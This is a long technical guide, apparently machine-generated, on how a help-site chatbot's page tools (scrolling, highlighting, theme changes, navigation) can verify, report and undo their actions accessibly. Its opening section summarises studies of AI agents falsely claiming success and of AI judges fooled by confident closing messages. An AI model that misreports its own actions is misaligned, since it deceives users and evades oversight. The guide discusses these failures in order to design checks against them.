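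In telecom tasks, where the simulated customer could check the state independently, only 3% of failures included a false claim. Advani thinks such checks may be an effective defence but says more environments of this kind are needed to be sure of the cause. On the help site, customers can see whether the page scrolled but not whether the site saved a setting to their account, so the handler needs to read the setting back to check.

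Having a second model read the conversation is a weak substitute for checking the page. Advani tested five models as judges, and none scored above 0.65, where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. The judges treated confident closing messages as evidence that the agent had done the job.

Users also encounter misreporting outside tests. In *Babysitting AI Agents* (2026), a study of user complaints, 679 cases (10.3%) concerned agents that had misreported their own actions. People rarely post about an agent that reported correctly, so the figure doesn't measure how often agents misreport.

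An agent may also act on its own false report. *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) describes an agent that clicked through a flight booking without checking the page after its clicks. It then put two flights in the user's real calendar, marked as confirmed, and told the user the booking was complete.

When only part of a task succeeds, the assistant should say which part. *HINTBench* (2026), a test of agents' mistakes, gives the example of an agent that tries to upload five files, succeeds with three, and reports all five as uploaded. It evaluates the action and the report separately. If the help site's theme changes but the scroll fails, the assistant did nothing wrong by trying, but it should report that the theme changed and the page didn't move.

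An action may have worked even if the call timed out. *Verified Tool Calls Improve LLM Agent Reliability Under Non-Atomic Failures* (2026) recommends checking whether the intended result is already in place before trying again. The assistant should also check before apologising for a failure. If `set_theme` times out, the code can read the current theme. If it can't, the assistant should say "I couldn't confirm that the theme changed."

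### Showing activity outside the reply

The software around the model can also show what the assistant is doing, without relying on the model to describe it. According to OpenAI, when a page offers site tools in the ChatGPT desktop app, an arrow appears in the address bar. It is grey when tools are available and blue while ChatGPT is using them. Selecting it shows the tools and whether each one can only read information or also make changes. Another button lists recently used tools. The conversation shows tool activity in chronological order, and the Sources view groups it by website.

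This helps a user notice when the model's reply leaves out an action or mentions one for which there was no call. It doesn't show whether a call worked, and OpenAI advises users to check the result on the page or in the conversation.

Morae reports its progress with different sounds for clicking, typing, questions, and completed actions. On request, a second model checks the result on the screen. Participants rated their awareness of results at 6.4 out of 7, compared with 4.6 with Operator. An embedded assistant should also tell people who use screen readers what it has changed.

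The help site's own code could use the handler's result to show a line such as "Theme changed to high contrast · Undo" under the assistant's reply. This line would be accurate even if the model described the change badly, but it would repeat any mistake in the handler's result. With the first version of `scrollToSection`, the customer would see the same false report in both the reply and the line.

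## Scrolling, highlighting and changing the theme

The "Undo" in a line such as "Theme changed to high contrast · Undo" works only if the handler saved the right information, called the *undo record*, before it changed anything. The record for a scroll, a highlight or a theme is tiny, but it is easy to save the wrong thing. For example, saving the scroll position in pixels or the name of the theme on screen can put the page back in the wrong state.

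### Scrolling to a section

The `scroll_to` handler finds a section by the `id` of its heading. Names become outdated when someone edits an article, so the page should build the tool's list of names from its current headings when it registers the tool.

The improved handler in the previous section puts the heading in the middle of the window, so whatever comes before the refund rules fills the top half. Putting the heading at the top shows more of the rules, but many sites keep a header bar fixed there. If the help site's bar is 32 pixels tall, it can cover the heading completely. The style rule `scroll-margin-top: 40px` on the headings makes the browser stop scrolling when the heading is 40 pixels from the top, just below the bar.

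That handler's check is also too loose. It returns `visible: true` whenever the heading lies inside the window, even if the header bar or the chat panel covers it. It does the same for a heading in a collapsed panel that the site hides with `display: none`, because the browser reports a hidden element's position as all zeros, and zero counts as inside the window. A better check looks up which element is on top at the heading's position:

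```js
heading.scrollIntoView({ behavior: "instant", block: "start" });
const box = heading.getBoundingClientRect();
const top = document.elementFromPoint(box.left + 5, box.top + box.height / 2);
return { section, visible: box.height > 0 && heading.contains(top) };
```

If the heading is in a collapsed panel, the handler has to open the panel first, and the undo record has to include that change too.

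Content can also load after the scroll. If a 300-pixel image loads above the refund rules, the rules move down by 300 pixels and the customer sees the end of the previous section instead. Browsers now correct for this with *scroll anchoring*. According to W3C's *CSS Scroll Anchoring Module Level 1*, a draft standard, the browser picks an element in view, compares its distance from the start of the content before and after the change, and scrolls by the difference.

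Safari was the last major browser to add scroll anchoring. WebKit's *News from WWDC26* (2026) announced it for Safari 27, and Modern CSS's browser-support page *overflow-anchor* lists it as available in every major browser since September 2026 and to 83% of users. Even with this support, the browser makes no correction when the page is at the very top, W3C lists operations that suppress the correction, and a site can switch it off. The handler should therefore measure the heading again once late images have loaded, and correct the position only if the customer hasn't scrolled in the meantime.

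### Returning to the same line

When the chatbot scrolls the page, the customer loses their place. The simplest way to restore it is to save the scroll position as a number and scroll back to it later, but this fails once the page changes length.

Suppose the customer has scrolled down 2,400 pixels and is reading a paragraph that starts 40 pixels below the top of the window, or 2,440 pixels from the top of the page. The assistant scrolls to the refund rules, and while the customer reads them, the site inserts a 300-pixel service outage notice near the top of the page.

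| | Before the notice | After the notice |
|---|---|---|
| Paragraph's distance from the top of the page | 2,440 | 2,740 |
| Scroll position that puts it 40 pixels below the top edge | 2,400 | 2,700 |

If the undo returns to 2,400, the paragraph is 340 pixels below the top edge, and the customer has to search for it. With a 1,000-pixel insertion, the paragraph would be off the screen on most laptops. Scroll anchoring doesn't help, because the browser corrects the current scroll position, not one that the site's code saved earlier.

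The handler should instead save the paragraph itself and its offset of 40 pixels. To undo the scroll, the code finds out where the paragraph is now and scrolls by the difference:

```js
function savePlace(el) {
  return { el, offset: el.getBoundingClientRect().top };
}
function returnTo({ el, offset }) {
  if (!el.isConnected) return { error: "that paragraph is gone" };
  const now = el.getBoundingClientRect().top;
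  window.scrollBy({ top: now - offset, behavior: "instant" });
  return { returned: true };
}
```

If the customer is at 5,400 when they press Undo, the paragraph is 2,660 pixels above the top edge, so `now` is −2,660. Subtracting the 40-pixel offset gives −2,700, which moves the page from 5,400 to 2,700, the right position. The result is the same wherever the customer has scrolled to.

The choice of element matters because if the handler saves a whole section and the notice appears inside it, above the paragraph, the section's top edge doesn't move and the undo is 300 pixels off again. For this reason, W3C has browsers prefer small, deeply nested elements. It also gives priority to a text field the user is typing in, and a site's own code can sensibly do the same.

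Two cases need more than an element and an offset. First, React and similar libraries sometimes replace a paragraph with an identical new one, so the saved reference points to an element no longer on the page. If the code also saves the paragraph's `id` or opening words, it can use those to find the new one. Second, the text size may change when the customer is halfway through a long paragraph. If the paragraph's top was 200 pixels above the edge and its height grows from 400 pixels to 600, the halfway point is now 300 pixels below its top. For paragraphs that begin above the edge, the code can save the fraction, here 0.5.

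### Highlighting a passage

When a customer asks how long they have to request a refund, highlighting the words "within 30 days" may help more than scrolling alone. The older way to highlight text is to wrap it in a `<mark>` element, which browsers show with a yellow background. Modern CSS's *Text highlighting without DOM manipulation* shows a typical version, which reads a section's HTML as text, puts `<mark>` around each match and writes the whole text back.

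Writing the HTML back makes the browser discard every element in the section and build new ones. Modern CSS notes that buttons lose the code that responds to clicks. In an ordinary HTML form, a text box also loses whatever the user has typed, because the HTML contains only the box's initial text. On the help site's long page, a request to highlight one word could erase the half-written complaint.

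The search also matches words inside HTML tags. Searching for "refund" turns the heading's `id` from `refund-rules` into `<mark>refund</mark>-rules`, so the next call to `scroll_to` returns an error. A link to `/refund-form` breaks in the same way.

More careful code wraps only the matching text. This still fails if the passage starts in one element and ends in another, for example when half of it is in bold. According to ics-creative, wrapping and unwrapping text can also break screen readers, text selection and third-party scripts that watch the page for changes. Removing the `<mark>` afterwards leaves the text in separate pieces unless the code joins them again.

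The CSS Custom Highlight API avoids all this. The code describes a range, meaning a start point and an end point in the text, and the browser paints it without changing the page's structure. A range can cross element boundaries. W3C's *CSS Custom Highlight API Module Level 1* (2021), a working draft, describes a registry in which each highlight has a name:

```js
const range = new Range();
range.setStart(startNode, startOffset);
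range.setEnd(endNode, endOffset);
CSS.highlights.set("assistant", new Highlight(range));
```

The code clears the highlight with `CSS.highlights.delete("assistant")`, because `clear()` would also remove the site's own highlights, such as matches from its search box. A new highlight from the assistant replaces any earlier one stored under the same name, so the handler should first save the earlier one for undo to restore. If there was no earlier highlight, undo has to delete the entry.

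Styles for these highlights can change colours and underlines but not the size or position of text, so nothing on the page moves. The text keeps its own colour unless the style sets one. The example in Modern CSS sets only a yellow background, so on a page with a dark theme it puts white text on yellow, which is very hard to read. The help site should set both the text and background colours.

The highlight can also vanish, because the browser ignores a range whose text has left the page and raises no error. If only the text around the passage changes, the browser adjusts an ordinary range to match. W3C also offers a fixed kind of range, which takes the browser less work but which the site has to replace after changes. For a single passage the ordinary kind is better, since a fixed range would save very little work.

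An accurate highlight may still mislead if it covers "within 30 days" and leaves out the exception in the next sentence.

Sometimes the assistant can give the customer a *text-fragment link* instead of using a tool. The link ends in `#:~:text=` followed by the words to find, as in `/billing#:~:text=within%2030%20days`. When the customer opens it, the browser scrolls to the first match and highlights it. If the same words appear several times, the link can include the words before or after the right passage. The customer decides whether and where to open the link. The browser hides the `:~:text=` part of the address from the page's scripts, so the site's code can't easily find out whether there was a match. If someone has since changed "within 30 days" to "within 14 days", the page opens with no highlight. The browser paints text-fragment highlights itself, so deleting an entry from the registry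 doesn't clear them.

### Changing the theme

Besides the blue gradient, CopilotKit has a theme example with a `setTheme` tool that accepts `light` or `dark`. The tool writes the value to the `data-theme` attribute on the page's root element and returns a message such as "Theme set to dark!". The site's styles then apply the colours for that value.

The handler doesn't read the old value before it writes the new one, so there is no saved value to restore. If the customer asks for the old theme back, the model can only infer it from the conversation. It might call `setTheme` with `light` because its last call set `dark`, even though the page may already have been dark before that call.

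Guessing fails more often than it might seem because most sites with a dark theme have three settings: light, dark, and matching the computer's theme, which many people have set to turn dark in the evening. Sites commonly store nothing for the third option.

| Preference | Stored value | Page at 4 pm, computer light | Page at 8 pm, computer dark |
|---|---|---|---|
| Light | `light` | Light | Light |
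| Dark | `dark` | Dark | Dark |
| Follow the system | None | Light | **Dark** |

If a customer has never chosen a theme, undoing a theme change should restore "no preference stored", so that the page follows the system setting again. Suppose the assistant switches the page to high contrast at 4 pm, the customer presses Undo, and the code sets the theme to `light`. The page looks as it did before, but when the computer switches to dark mode at 8 pm, the help site stays light. `setTheme` can't restore the original state, even if the model has a record of it, because the tool accepts only two values and neither means "follow the system".

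A handler that saves the earlier state needs only a few more lines:

```js
let undoTheme = null;
function setTheme({ theme }) {
  const root = document.documentElement;
  const before = root.getAttribute("data-theme");
  root.setAttribute("data-theme", theme);
  undoTheme = () => {
    if (before === null) root.removeAttribute("data-theme");
    else root.setAttribute("data-theme", before);
  };
  return { theme };
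}
```

If the page had no `data-theme` attribute, `before` is `null`, and the undo removes the attribute. Writing `null` back would set the attribute to the string "null", which matches none of the site's themes. Local storage, where many sites save the preference, converts `null` the same way, so an undo there would have to call `removeItem`. The code above doesn't change local storage, which suits a request to make "this" easier to read.

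The customer can also lose their place because the high-contrast theme enlarges the text. The handler should save their place before changing the theme and restore it afterwards, as with a scroll. It should do the same when undoing the theme, because that moves the text again.

If the site's settings menu keeps its own record of the theme, writing the attribute directly leaves the menu showing "Light" on a dark page, and the site may restore the old value the next time it redraws. The safest handler calls the same function the menu calls. Some users set their operating system to replace every site's colours with a high-contrast set. For them, `set_theme` may change the attribute with almost no visible effect, so the chatbot should not promise a visible change.

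### Moving the page while someone reads or types

After sending the request, the customer may go back to typing the complaint and be partway through a sentence when the handler runs. If the page then scrolls to the refund rules, the text box moves off the screen while they are typing. Their keystrokes still go to the box, and most browsers scroll back to it at the next letter, so the page jumps twice.

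The harm is worse if the handler also moves the *keyboard focus*, the point on the page that receives keystrokes. The rest of the sentence the user is typing is then lost, and pressing the space bar scrolls the page or, if the focus is on a button, activates the button.

When the page jumps, someone who is only reading loses their place, and some people find it much harder than others to recover. A person with low vision who magnifies the screen may see only a few lines at a time, so after a jump nothing familiar is in view. W3C's *Understanding SC 3.2.5 Change on Request (Level AAA)* also lists people who are blind, people with motor impairments and people with certain cognitive limitations among those affected by unexpected changes.

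An unwanted scroll is worse for these customers, so the assistant should be more certain before it scrolls on a guess. If the loss is 3 instead of 1, the threshold in the earlier example rises from 0.25 to 0.5. A site can't reliably detect these customers, but it can offer everyone a setting that stops the assistant from moving the page.

The handler can also check whether the customer has pressed a key in a text box outside the chat in the last few seconds. If so, it should leave the page where it is and return `{ "moved": false, "reason": "user is typing" }`. The reply can then include a button labelled "Go to the refund rules".

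### Keyboard focus

When the chatbot scrolls the page to the refund rules, the keyboard focus stays in the chat box. If the customer then presses Tab, they go to the next control after the chat box, which may be far from the refund rules. A screen reader, the software that reads pages aloud to people who can't see them, generally stays where it was too, so the reply "You're now at the refund rules" would then be false for a blind customer.

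After a request such as "Take me there", the handler should move the focus to the heading. Headings don't normally accept focus, but setting `tabindex` to −1 lets code focus one without adding it to the Tab order. The undo record must then also store which element had the focus before. If the customer asked only where the rules are, the focus should stay in the chat, because they may want to ask something else.

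The Web Content Accessibility Guidelines (WCAG) treat moving the focus as a *change of context*, which W3C defines as a major change that, if made without users' awareness, can disorient those who can't see the whole page at once. The current version, WCAG 2.2, dates from October 2023. Its criterion 3.2.5, at AAA, the strictest of three levels, requires that "changes of context are initiated only by user request" or that "a mechanism is available to turn off such changes". The setting that stops the assistant from moving the page is such a mechanism.

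It is less clear whether scrolling without moving the focus also counts as a change of context. The definition includes a change of viewport, but W3C uses that word for the window or frame that shows the content, and its example is a link that opens a new window. On a strict reading, scrolling within the same window doesn't count. But it can disorient people in the same way, so it makes little sense for the help site to apply a looser rule to it.

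Clicking a link is a request for the new content, but according to W3C, a new window is not user-initiated unless the user explicitly asked for it. By that reasoning, "Take me to the refund rules" covers scrolling to the rules and moving the focus there, but not opening a second tab.

Criterion 3.2.2 applies at level A, so even sites that aim only for the minimum have to meet it. In the wording quoted by *Decoding WCAG*, from the web accessibility organisation WebAIM, changing a control's setting must "not automatically cause a change of context" unless the site has told the user beforehand. WebAIM points out that activating a button or link is more than a change of setting. Pressing Enter in the chat is therefore a request, but an assistant that jumped to the refund rules as soon as the customer had typed "refu" would probably fail the criterion.

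A fixed header can also hide the control that has the focus. Criterion 2.4.11, added in version 2.2 at level AA, requires that a focused control "is not entirely hidden due to author-created content". UTMB's *Web Content Accessibility Guidelines (WCAG) 2.2*, a university's copy of the criteria, includes an exception for content that the user opened, provided the user can uncover the control without advancing the focus. A chat panel that the user opened could therefore cover a form field the assistant has just focused, as long as a key such as Escape closes the panel without moving the focus.

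### Motion

Movement on a screen can cause dizziness and nausea in people with vestibular disorders, which affect the inner ear and balance. W3C's *Understanding Animation from Interactions*, an early draft, lists migraine among the effects and says they can be severe enough to need bed rest. Criterion 2.3.3, at level AAA, requires that "motion animation triggered by interaction can be disabled" unless it is "essential to the functionality or the information being conveyed".

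Deque University's *2.3.3 Animations from Interactions (AAA)* treats basic page scrolling as essential and therefore exempt, and BATI-ITAO's accessibility course *Animation and motion* explains that scrolling is allowed because the user controls the movement. When an assistant smoothly scrolls through 3,000 pixels of text after a typed request, the user no longer controls the movement, so the exemption is a weak defence for that animation.

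An instant jump avoids the problem because it has no animation. Setting `behavior: "instant"` in the handler also overrides any smooth scrolling that the site's styles set for the whole page. Smooth scrolling shows sighted users which way the page moved, but after an instant jump, a brief highlight on the heading can help them see where they are. If the developers still want smooth scrolling, the handler should first check the browser's `prefers-reduced-motion` value, which reflects a setting in the user's operating system, according to the NHS's *Animation respects reduce-motion settings*.

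A pulsing highlight needs a time limit. W3C's *Understanding SC 2.2.2 Pause, Stop, Hide (Level A)* explains that users must be able to pause, stop or hide movement or blinking that starts automatically, lasts more than five seconds and appears alongside other content. This requirement doesn't apply to a steady yellow highlight.

### Status messages

A customer who can't see the page turn dark depends on the screen reader to announce the line "Theme changed to high contrast". Criterion 4.1.3, at level AA, requires that status messages "can be programmatically determined through role or properties" so that assistive technology can present them "without receiving focus". W3C's *Understanding SC 4.1.3 Status Messages (Level AA)* recommends labelling the element that holds the message with `role="status"`, so that the screen reader can read the line aloud while the customer stays in the chat box.

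The criterion requires a site to label the status messages it shows, but not to create any. A site could therefore meet it without showing a message after a theme change, which would leave blind customers with no independent report of what the assistant did.

Too many announcements are also a problem. If both the assistant's reply and the site's message announce the theme change, the customer hears it twice. W3C warns against making a page too "chatty" and recommends testing with users. In its accessibility guidance, the State of Minnesota says one message area is often better than several. It also distinguishes polite announcements, which wait for a pause, from assertive ones, which the screen reader reads at once. A theme change should use a polite announcement.

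When the handler moves the focus to the refund rules, no status message is necessary, because screen readers already announce a change of focus. After a highlight, the message should include the highlighted words. The W3C draft recommends, but does not require, that browsers expose custom highlights to assistive technology, so a screen reader may not mention the highlight.

When a customer presses Undo, the site should replace the line "Theme changed to high contrast" with "Previous theme restored". If the line just disappears, a sighted customer sees the old colours return, but a screen reader may announce nothing. The site should also mark the whole sentence as one message, because otherwise the screen reader may read out only the words that changed.

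## Opening another page without losing the user's work

Many help sites keep the refund rules and the complaint form on separate pages, so the assistant has to leave one to show the other. Whether the user loses a half-written complaint depends mostly on how the refund page opens.

### Five ways to reach the refund rules

A jump within the page only scrolls to another part of it. In a *single-page application*, the site's code redraws part of the page instead of loading a new one. A *route change* in such a site replaces the form with the refund rules and updates the address. A full page load replaces everything in the tab. The assistant can also open a new tab or send the customer to a page on another website, such as the payment company's refund policy.

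| Kind of navigation | The complaint | The conversation | What Back does |
|---|---|---|---|
| Jump within the page | Stays in the form | Stays | Returns to the earlier position, if the jump added a history entry |
| Route change | Gone, unless the site's code keeps it | Stays, if the chat panel is outside the part that changes | The site redraws the form, often empty |
| Full page load | Returns if the browser kept the old page | Disappears until the new page loads it again | Revives the old page or loads it afresh |
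| New tab | Stays in the old tab | Stays in the old tab | Nothing, because the new tab has no earlier page |
| Another site | As with a full page load | Gone until the customer returns | As with a full page load |

A route change can lose the user's work because the site's own code removes the form. The address and the Back button behave as if a new page had loaded, but the browser has kept the same page. The documentation of Svelte, another set of tools for building websites, warns that a user who half-fills a form, navigates away and comes back will find it empty. Svelte's remedy is a *snapshot*, for which the developer writes a function that copies the form's contents just before the page updates. Svelte stores the copy with the history entry and returns it when the user comes back.

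### What the Back button returns to

Each tab keeps a list of *history entries*, which Back and Forward step through. WHATWG's *Navigation and session history*, part of the HTML standard that browsers follow, distinguishes a *push*, which adds an entry, from a *replace*, which overwrites the current one. Suppose the customer found the support form through a web search:

| How the refund page opens | The tab's history | Back leads to |
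|---|---|---|
| Push | Search results, support form, **refund rules** | Support form |
| Replace | Search results, **refund rules** | Search results |

A handler that opens the page with `location.replace()` therefore removes the way back to the complaint. Pushing a new history entry does less harm, but it permanently erases any pages the customer could still have reached with Forward.

The `scroll_to` handler from the previous section calls `scrollIntoView`, which doesn't change the browser history. But a customer who sees the page jump may well press Back to undo it, which takes them away from the complaint to the search results. The handler can prevent this by adding a history entry with `history.pushState(null, "", "#refund-rules")` before it scrolls, so that Back returns to the form. If the assistant scrolls again straight away, the handler should replace that entry, or the customer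 will have to press Back once for every scroll.

An Undo button that calls `history.back()` moves the customer back one step from the page they are on now. If they have followed a link from the refund rules to an article on bank transfers, it returns them to the refund rules, not the form. Each history entry also has a random key, so the handler can save the form's key before leaving, and the button can go straight to the form with `navigation.traverseTo(key)`. This only reaches entries in an unbroken run of pages from the same site. A new tab has no earlier page to go back to. According to MDN, a reference site for web developers, a request to move past the end of the history list silently does nothing, so the Undo button shouldn't announce success there.

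Chrome's Back button also skips any page that added a history entry or redirected the user before the user had clicked, tapped or typed anything on it. According to the documentation for Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome, this rule is meant to stop sites from trapping visitors. If the assistant opens a billing overview and immediately moves on to the refund rules, Back goes directly to the form, which is probably what the customer wants.

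In a single-page application, the rule can work against the customer. Suppose they send a request, press Back to an earlier article while the model is still working, and the route change arrives afterwards. Chromium ignores their earlier typing when deciding whether to skip the new entry, and it treats all entries of the same page alike, so the next press of Back can leave the help site unless they click or type first. Before changing the route, the handler could check that the customer is still on the page where they made the request. Juma (2021), in *History intervention to prevent Back button abuse*, reported that Firefox's engine also skipped such entries, but Safari did not at the time.

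The Back button normally restores the scroll position as well. In a single-page application, the browser may try this before the site has redrawn the old content, when the page is still too short to scroll that far. A site can set `history.scrollRestoration` to `manual`, and Chrome for Developers' *History API* explains that the developer is then responsible for restoring the position. The saved paragraph and offset described in the previous section work well for this, as long as the code saves the paragraph's `id`, because the redrawn paragraph is a new element.

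### The page the browser keeps in memory

After a full page load, the customer's best chance of recovering the complaint is the *back/forward cache*. Every major browser has one, according to Google's web.dev guide *Back/forward cache*. When the customer leaves a page, the browser freezes it in memory, including its running code, and restores it if the customer soon presses Back. The complaint then reappears as the customer left it, even if the editor saves nothing.

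However, the browser can drop the frozen page at any time. Chrome keeps it for at most ten minutes, or three if the server marked the page `no-store`, according to Chrome for Developers' *Enabling bfcache for Cache-Control* (2024). Sites often send `no-store`, which tells browsers not to keep copies, with pages behind a login. Other browsers may not keep `no-store` pages at all. A signed-in customer who reads the refund rules for four minutes could therefore return to a form that Chrome has to load again. Their text may not come back, because WHATWG lets each browser decide whether to store what users typed into forms.

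The chatbot's own code may keep the page out of the cache. On desktop, Chrome and Firefox exclude any page that runs code on the old `unload` event, even if the code came from another company's chat widget. Some browsers also exclude pages with certain open connections, which a chat panel may use to receive replies. In a 2014 report in Mozilla's bug tracker, someone edited text on a test page, left, pressed Back and found the original text, because an `unload` handler had blocked the cache. With the handler disabled, the edits survived. web.dev advises closing connections on the `pagehide` event and reopening them if the page returns.

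Freezing a page also stops its timers. If the site saves a draft two seconds after the last keystroke and the assistant opens another page after one second, the save runs only if the customer returns before the browser discards the frozen page. The site's code should save the draft immediately on `pagehide`.

### Bringing the conversation along

The chat panel is part of the page, so a full page load erases it too. The site usually keeps the messages on its server and a conversation identifier in the browser, and the new page uses the identifier to reload the messages. *Session storage* suits the identifier because it belongs to a single tab. If the identifier were in *local storage*, which all the site's tabs share, two support tabs would write into one conversation, and the model could confuse one page's contents with the other's.

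When a tool call opens another page, the handler's page is gone before it can return a result. If the old page reports success before leaving, it does so before the new page has opened. The handler can instead save the call's identifier in session storage, and the new page can send the result after checking that the refund rules are there.

When the user presses Back, the browser restores the support page with the chat panel as it was, without the messages from the refund page. It also fires a `pageshow` event whose `persisted` value is true, and the panel can then fetch the missing messages.

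When a browser agent opens another page, its conversation continues because it is outside the page, but the first page's tools are lost. Search Engine Journal notes that WebMCP tools last only as long as their tab. On Shopify's shops, these tools act in the customer's active tab, so a page the agent opens replaces whatever the customer had there.

### Why the new tab should be a link

A new tab leaves the page with the complaint open and unchanged, so it is the safest choice when the site can't save a draft. But a handler may have trouble opening one, because browsers generally let code open a tab only shortly after a click or key press, and the model may take several seconds to respond.

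Checking whether the tab opened is also a problem. `window.open()` normally returns a reference to the new tab, which the handler could test, but while that reference exists, neither page is eligible for the back/forward cache. The `noopener` option avoids this connection, but the function then returns `null` whether or not the tab opened.

A link in the chat labelled "Refund rules (opens in a new tab)" avoids both problems. The customer's click is the recent user action the browser requires, and modern browsers apply `noopener` by default to links that open a new tab. Because the label says that a new tab will open, the click also counts as the explicit request that, in W3C's view, a new window needs.

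### An experiment with lost drafts

*Can You Undo It?* includes one of the few direct tests of whether a lost draft can be recovered. The researchers put two short made-up drafts into five kinds of editor, closed the tab, and tried to recover the text by opening the address again or using the browser's command for reopening a closed tab. They did this in Chromium 158, Firefox 160 and Safari 18.5, and got the same results when they repeated every case.

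| Editor | Opening the address, all three browsers | Reopening the tab, Chromium and Firefox | Reopening the tab, Safari |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain text box, nothing saved | Empty | Final text | Empty |
| Plain text box, copy in session storage | Empty | Final text | Empty |
| Plain text box, saved to local storage on every input | Final text | Final text | Final text |
| Plain text box, only the first edit saved to local storage | First edit only | Final text | First edit only |
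| Rich-text editor, nothing saved | Empty | Empty | Empty |

Saving on every input was the only method that recovered the final text on both routes in all three browsers. The fourth row may be the most dangerous, because a customer who sees their opening sentences back in the box may assume the rest is there and submit an incomplete complaint. A developer who tests only by reopening a tab in Chrome would miss the problem, because the browser's own recovery restores the missing text.

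The researchers also restarted Chromium and Firefox. The text saved on every input came back in full with the same user profile, but none of it came back with a separate profile. Local storage therefore won't help a customer who starts on a phone and continues on a laptop. That customer needs a draft saved on the server, which the experiment didn't test. It also didn't test a rich-text editor with autosave, which would probably give the same result as the third row if the site saved the formatted text.

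The gap between Safari and the other two browsers is weak evidence of a difference between the browsers themselves. The researchers operated Safari by hand through its menus but ran the others automatically, without a visible window. Safari 18.5 was also an old release by November 2026.

More importantly for the help site, the experiment closed tabs and did not test leaving a page and pressing Back in the same tab. web.dev lists reopening a closed tab as a case where the back/forward cache doesn't apply, so text in the rich-text editor that came back empty in the last row might well survive Back. The results for opening the address better indicate what happens when that cache is gone and the customer follows a link to the form. Even so, a rule that treats "close tab" as one action with one level of risk, as the paper's list of tools does, can't be right for every editor.

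### The limits of the leave-page warning

Browsers can ask "Leave site?" before a page closes. A site requests this by responding to the `beforeunload` event, and web.dev recommends doing so only while the user has unsaved work. It is a useful last resort for the help site, but it has many gaps:

- It covers full page loads and closed tabs. makandra's *How to display an unsaved changes alert*, a developer's note, points out that the event doesn't fire when code changes the route, which is the case where the browser keeps no copy of the form.
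- The browser chooses the wording, so the warning can't mention the complaint or offer to open a new tab.
- Safari on iPhones and iPads doesn't fire the event. Dumez (2020) reported this in *beforeunload event does not fire in MobileSafari*. WebKit added a fix that November and withdrew it weeks later because it seemed to harm a performance test, and users were still asking for one in April 2026.
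- Safari on the Mac had a gap as well. Niwa (2025), in *Safari does not show beforeunload prompt when navigating cross site*, described a failure on moves to other websites, which WebKit fixed that April.
- The event doesn't fire if the system shuts down a background tab, according to Chrome for Developers' *Deprecating the unload event*.

Chrome also shows the warning only if the user has interacted with the page. Drissman (2017), in *Intent to Implement and Ship*, justified this rule by calling the dialog "inherently user-hostile", since it makes users confirm a request they have just made. According to MDN's *Sticky activation*, key presses, mouse presses and touches since the page loaded count as interaction, but scrolling doesn't. A customer who typed a complaint meets the condition. But if the assistant opens the support page, fills in the form from the conversation, and moves to another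 page by itself, the customer hasn't interacted with the support page, so Chrome discards the text without a warning.

When the warning does appear, the customer may choose to stay on the page. The handler gets no error in that case, so if it is still running a few seconds after asking the browser to leave, it should report that the new page didn't open.

### Before the assistant leaves the page

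The help site can do better than the browser's warning because its own code can tell what the customer would lose. The handler should work through these steps:

1. Check for unsaved work. If there is none, open the page.
2. Save a draft and read it back. If the copy matches, open the page and tell the customer that the complaint is saved.
3. If the draft can't be saved, stay on the page and offer a link that opens in a new tab. A single-page application that can't do this should ask before it removes the form.
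4. Leave only after one of these steps has succeeded or the customer has agreed to lose the text.

For a form with one text box, the code is short:

```js
function saveDraft(text) {
  try {
    localStorage.setItem("complaint-draft", text);
    return localStorage.getItem("complaint-draft") === text;
  } catch {
    return false;
  }
}
function openArticle({ article }) {
  const url = articles.get(article);
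  if (!url) return { error: "unknown article" };
  const text = complaint.value;
  if (text !== complaint.defaultValue && !saveDraft(text)) {
    return { opened: false, reason: "unsaved complaint", link: url };
  }
  location.assign(url);
  return { leaving: true };
}
```

`defaultValue` is the text the page first put in the box, so if the current text differs, the customer has typed something. This check doesn't work for rich-text editors, which have no `defaultValue`. It also fails when React updates `defaultValue` as the customer types, as it often does, because the two values then always match. Such sites need their own record of the last saved text. The software around the handler should treat `leaving` as unfinished and wait for the new page's report, as described above.

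The support page must also put the saved draft back when it loads, but only if the box is empty. Otherwise, an old draft could overwrite newer text that the browser has already restored. An empty form in a second tab must not overwrite the saved draft.

The site should also save on every input, as in the third row of the experiment, not only when its own assistant is about to leave the page, because `openArticle` is never called when a browser agent types a new address into the tab or a customer closes the tab by accident.

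Saved drafts create a privacy risk. A complaint about a double charge may contain card details or an address, and the next person to use a library computer could find it in the form. The site should delete the draft when the customer submits it or signs out, or after a few days if they do neither.

Once the refund page is open, the assistant can write, "I've opened the refund rules. Your complaint is saved, and Back returns to it." If the form is on a route the site created with `pushState`, the developers should check that its address also works when loaded from the server. Flavio Copes' *History API* warns that a refresh or browser restart requests that address directly, and a server without a page there returns an error, even when the site has saved the draft.

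### Links that do more than open a page

Opening an address can change something on the server, even though the HTTP specification says it shouldn't. Following a link sends a GET request, while many forms send a POST request. *HTTP safety doesn't happen by accident*, an article from the software consultancy thoughtbot, quotes the specification, which calls a method "safe" if its meaning is "essentially read-only". GET is safe in this sense and POST is not. *The HTTP QUERY Method* (2025), a draft from the IETF, which maintains HTTP, classifies them the same way.

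A "safe" request asks only to read data, but the server can still change something in response. Some sites sign a user out, cancel a subscription or confirm an email address through a plain link. MDN's *Safe (HTTP Methods)* adds that browsers rely on this convention when they fetch pages in advance, so these changes can happen before anyone clicks.

If the customer asks the assistant "Where do I sign out?" and the model opens `/logout` to show them, it signs them out. Pressing Back doesn't sign them in again. It may not recover the complaint either, because Chrome discards a frozen `no-store` page when the site's cookies change, as they do at sign-out. A handler that fetches `/logout` in the background to check that the page exists would also sign the customer out.

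The help site's developers can avoid this in their own tools by letting `open_article` accept only article names. They should also put sign-out and similar actions behind a button that sends a POST request, which protects customers whose browser agents follow links without using the site's tools. The developers can't check what a GET request does on other sites, and the address itself can carry private data to whoever runs the site. For links to other sites, the assistant should show the customer the full link and let them open it.

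## Undoing what the assistant did

The help site's code now saves the customer's place before it scrolls, the old theme before it changes the colours, and the draft before it leaves the page. One Undo button can restore all of these, but it must not erase anything the customer has done since.

### Why interfaces offer undo

In *Direct Manipulation* (1983), Ben Shneiderman tried to explain why some programs delighted people and others were only grudgingly accepted. In the programs people liked, users could see the object they were working on, act on it directly instead of typing commands, and work in quick, small steps that they could reverse. For example, someone who moves a spaceship too far left in a video game can move it right again. Shneiderman also thought that people worry less about destroying a file when they can easily undo a mistake.

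Ben Shneiderman's favourite example of direct manipulation was driving, where the driver turns the wheel, watches the road and corrects. He asked readers to imagine steering by typing "LEFT 30 DEGREES" and then entering another command to check the car's position. Asking a chatbot to change a page is closer to typing commands. The customer can't correct the change along the way and sees the result only when it is complete, so being able to undo it matters more.

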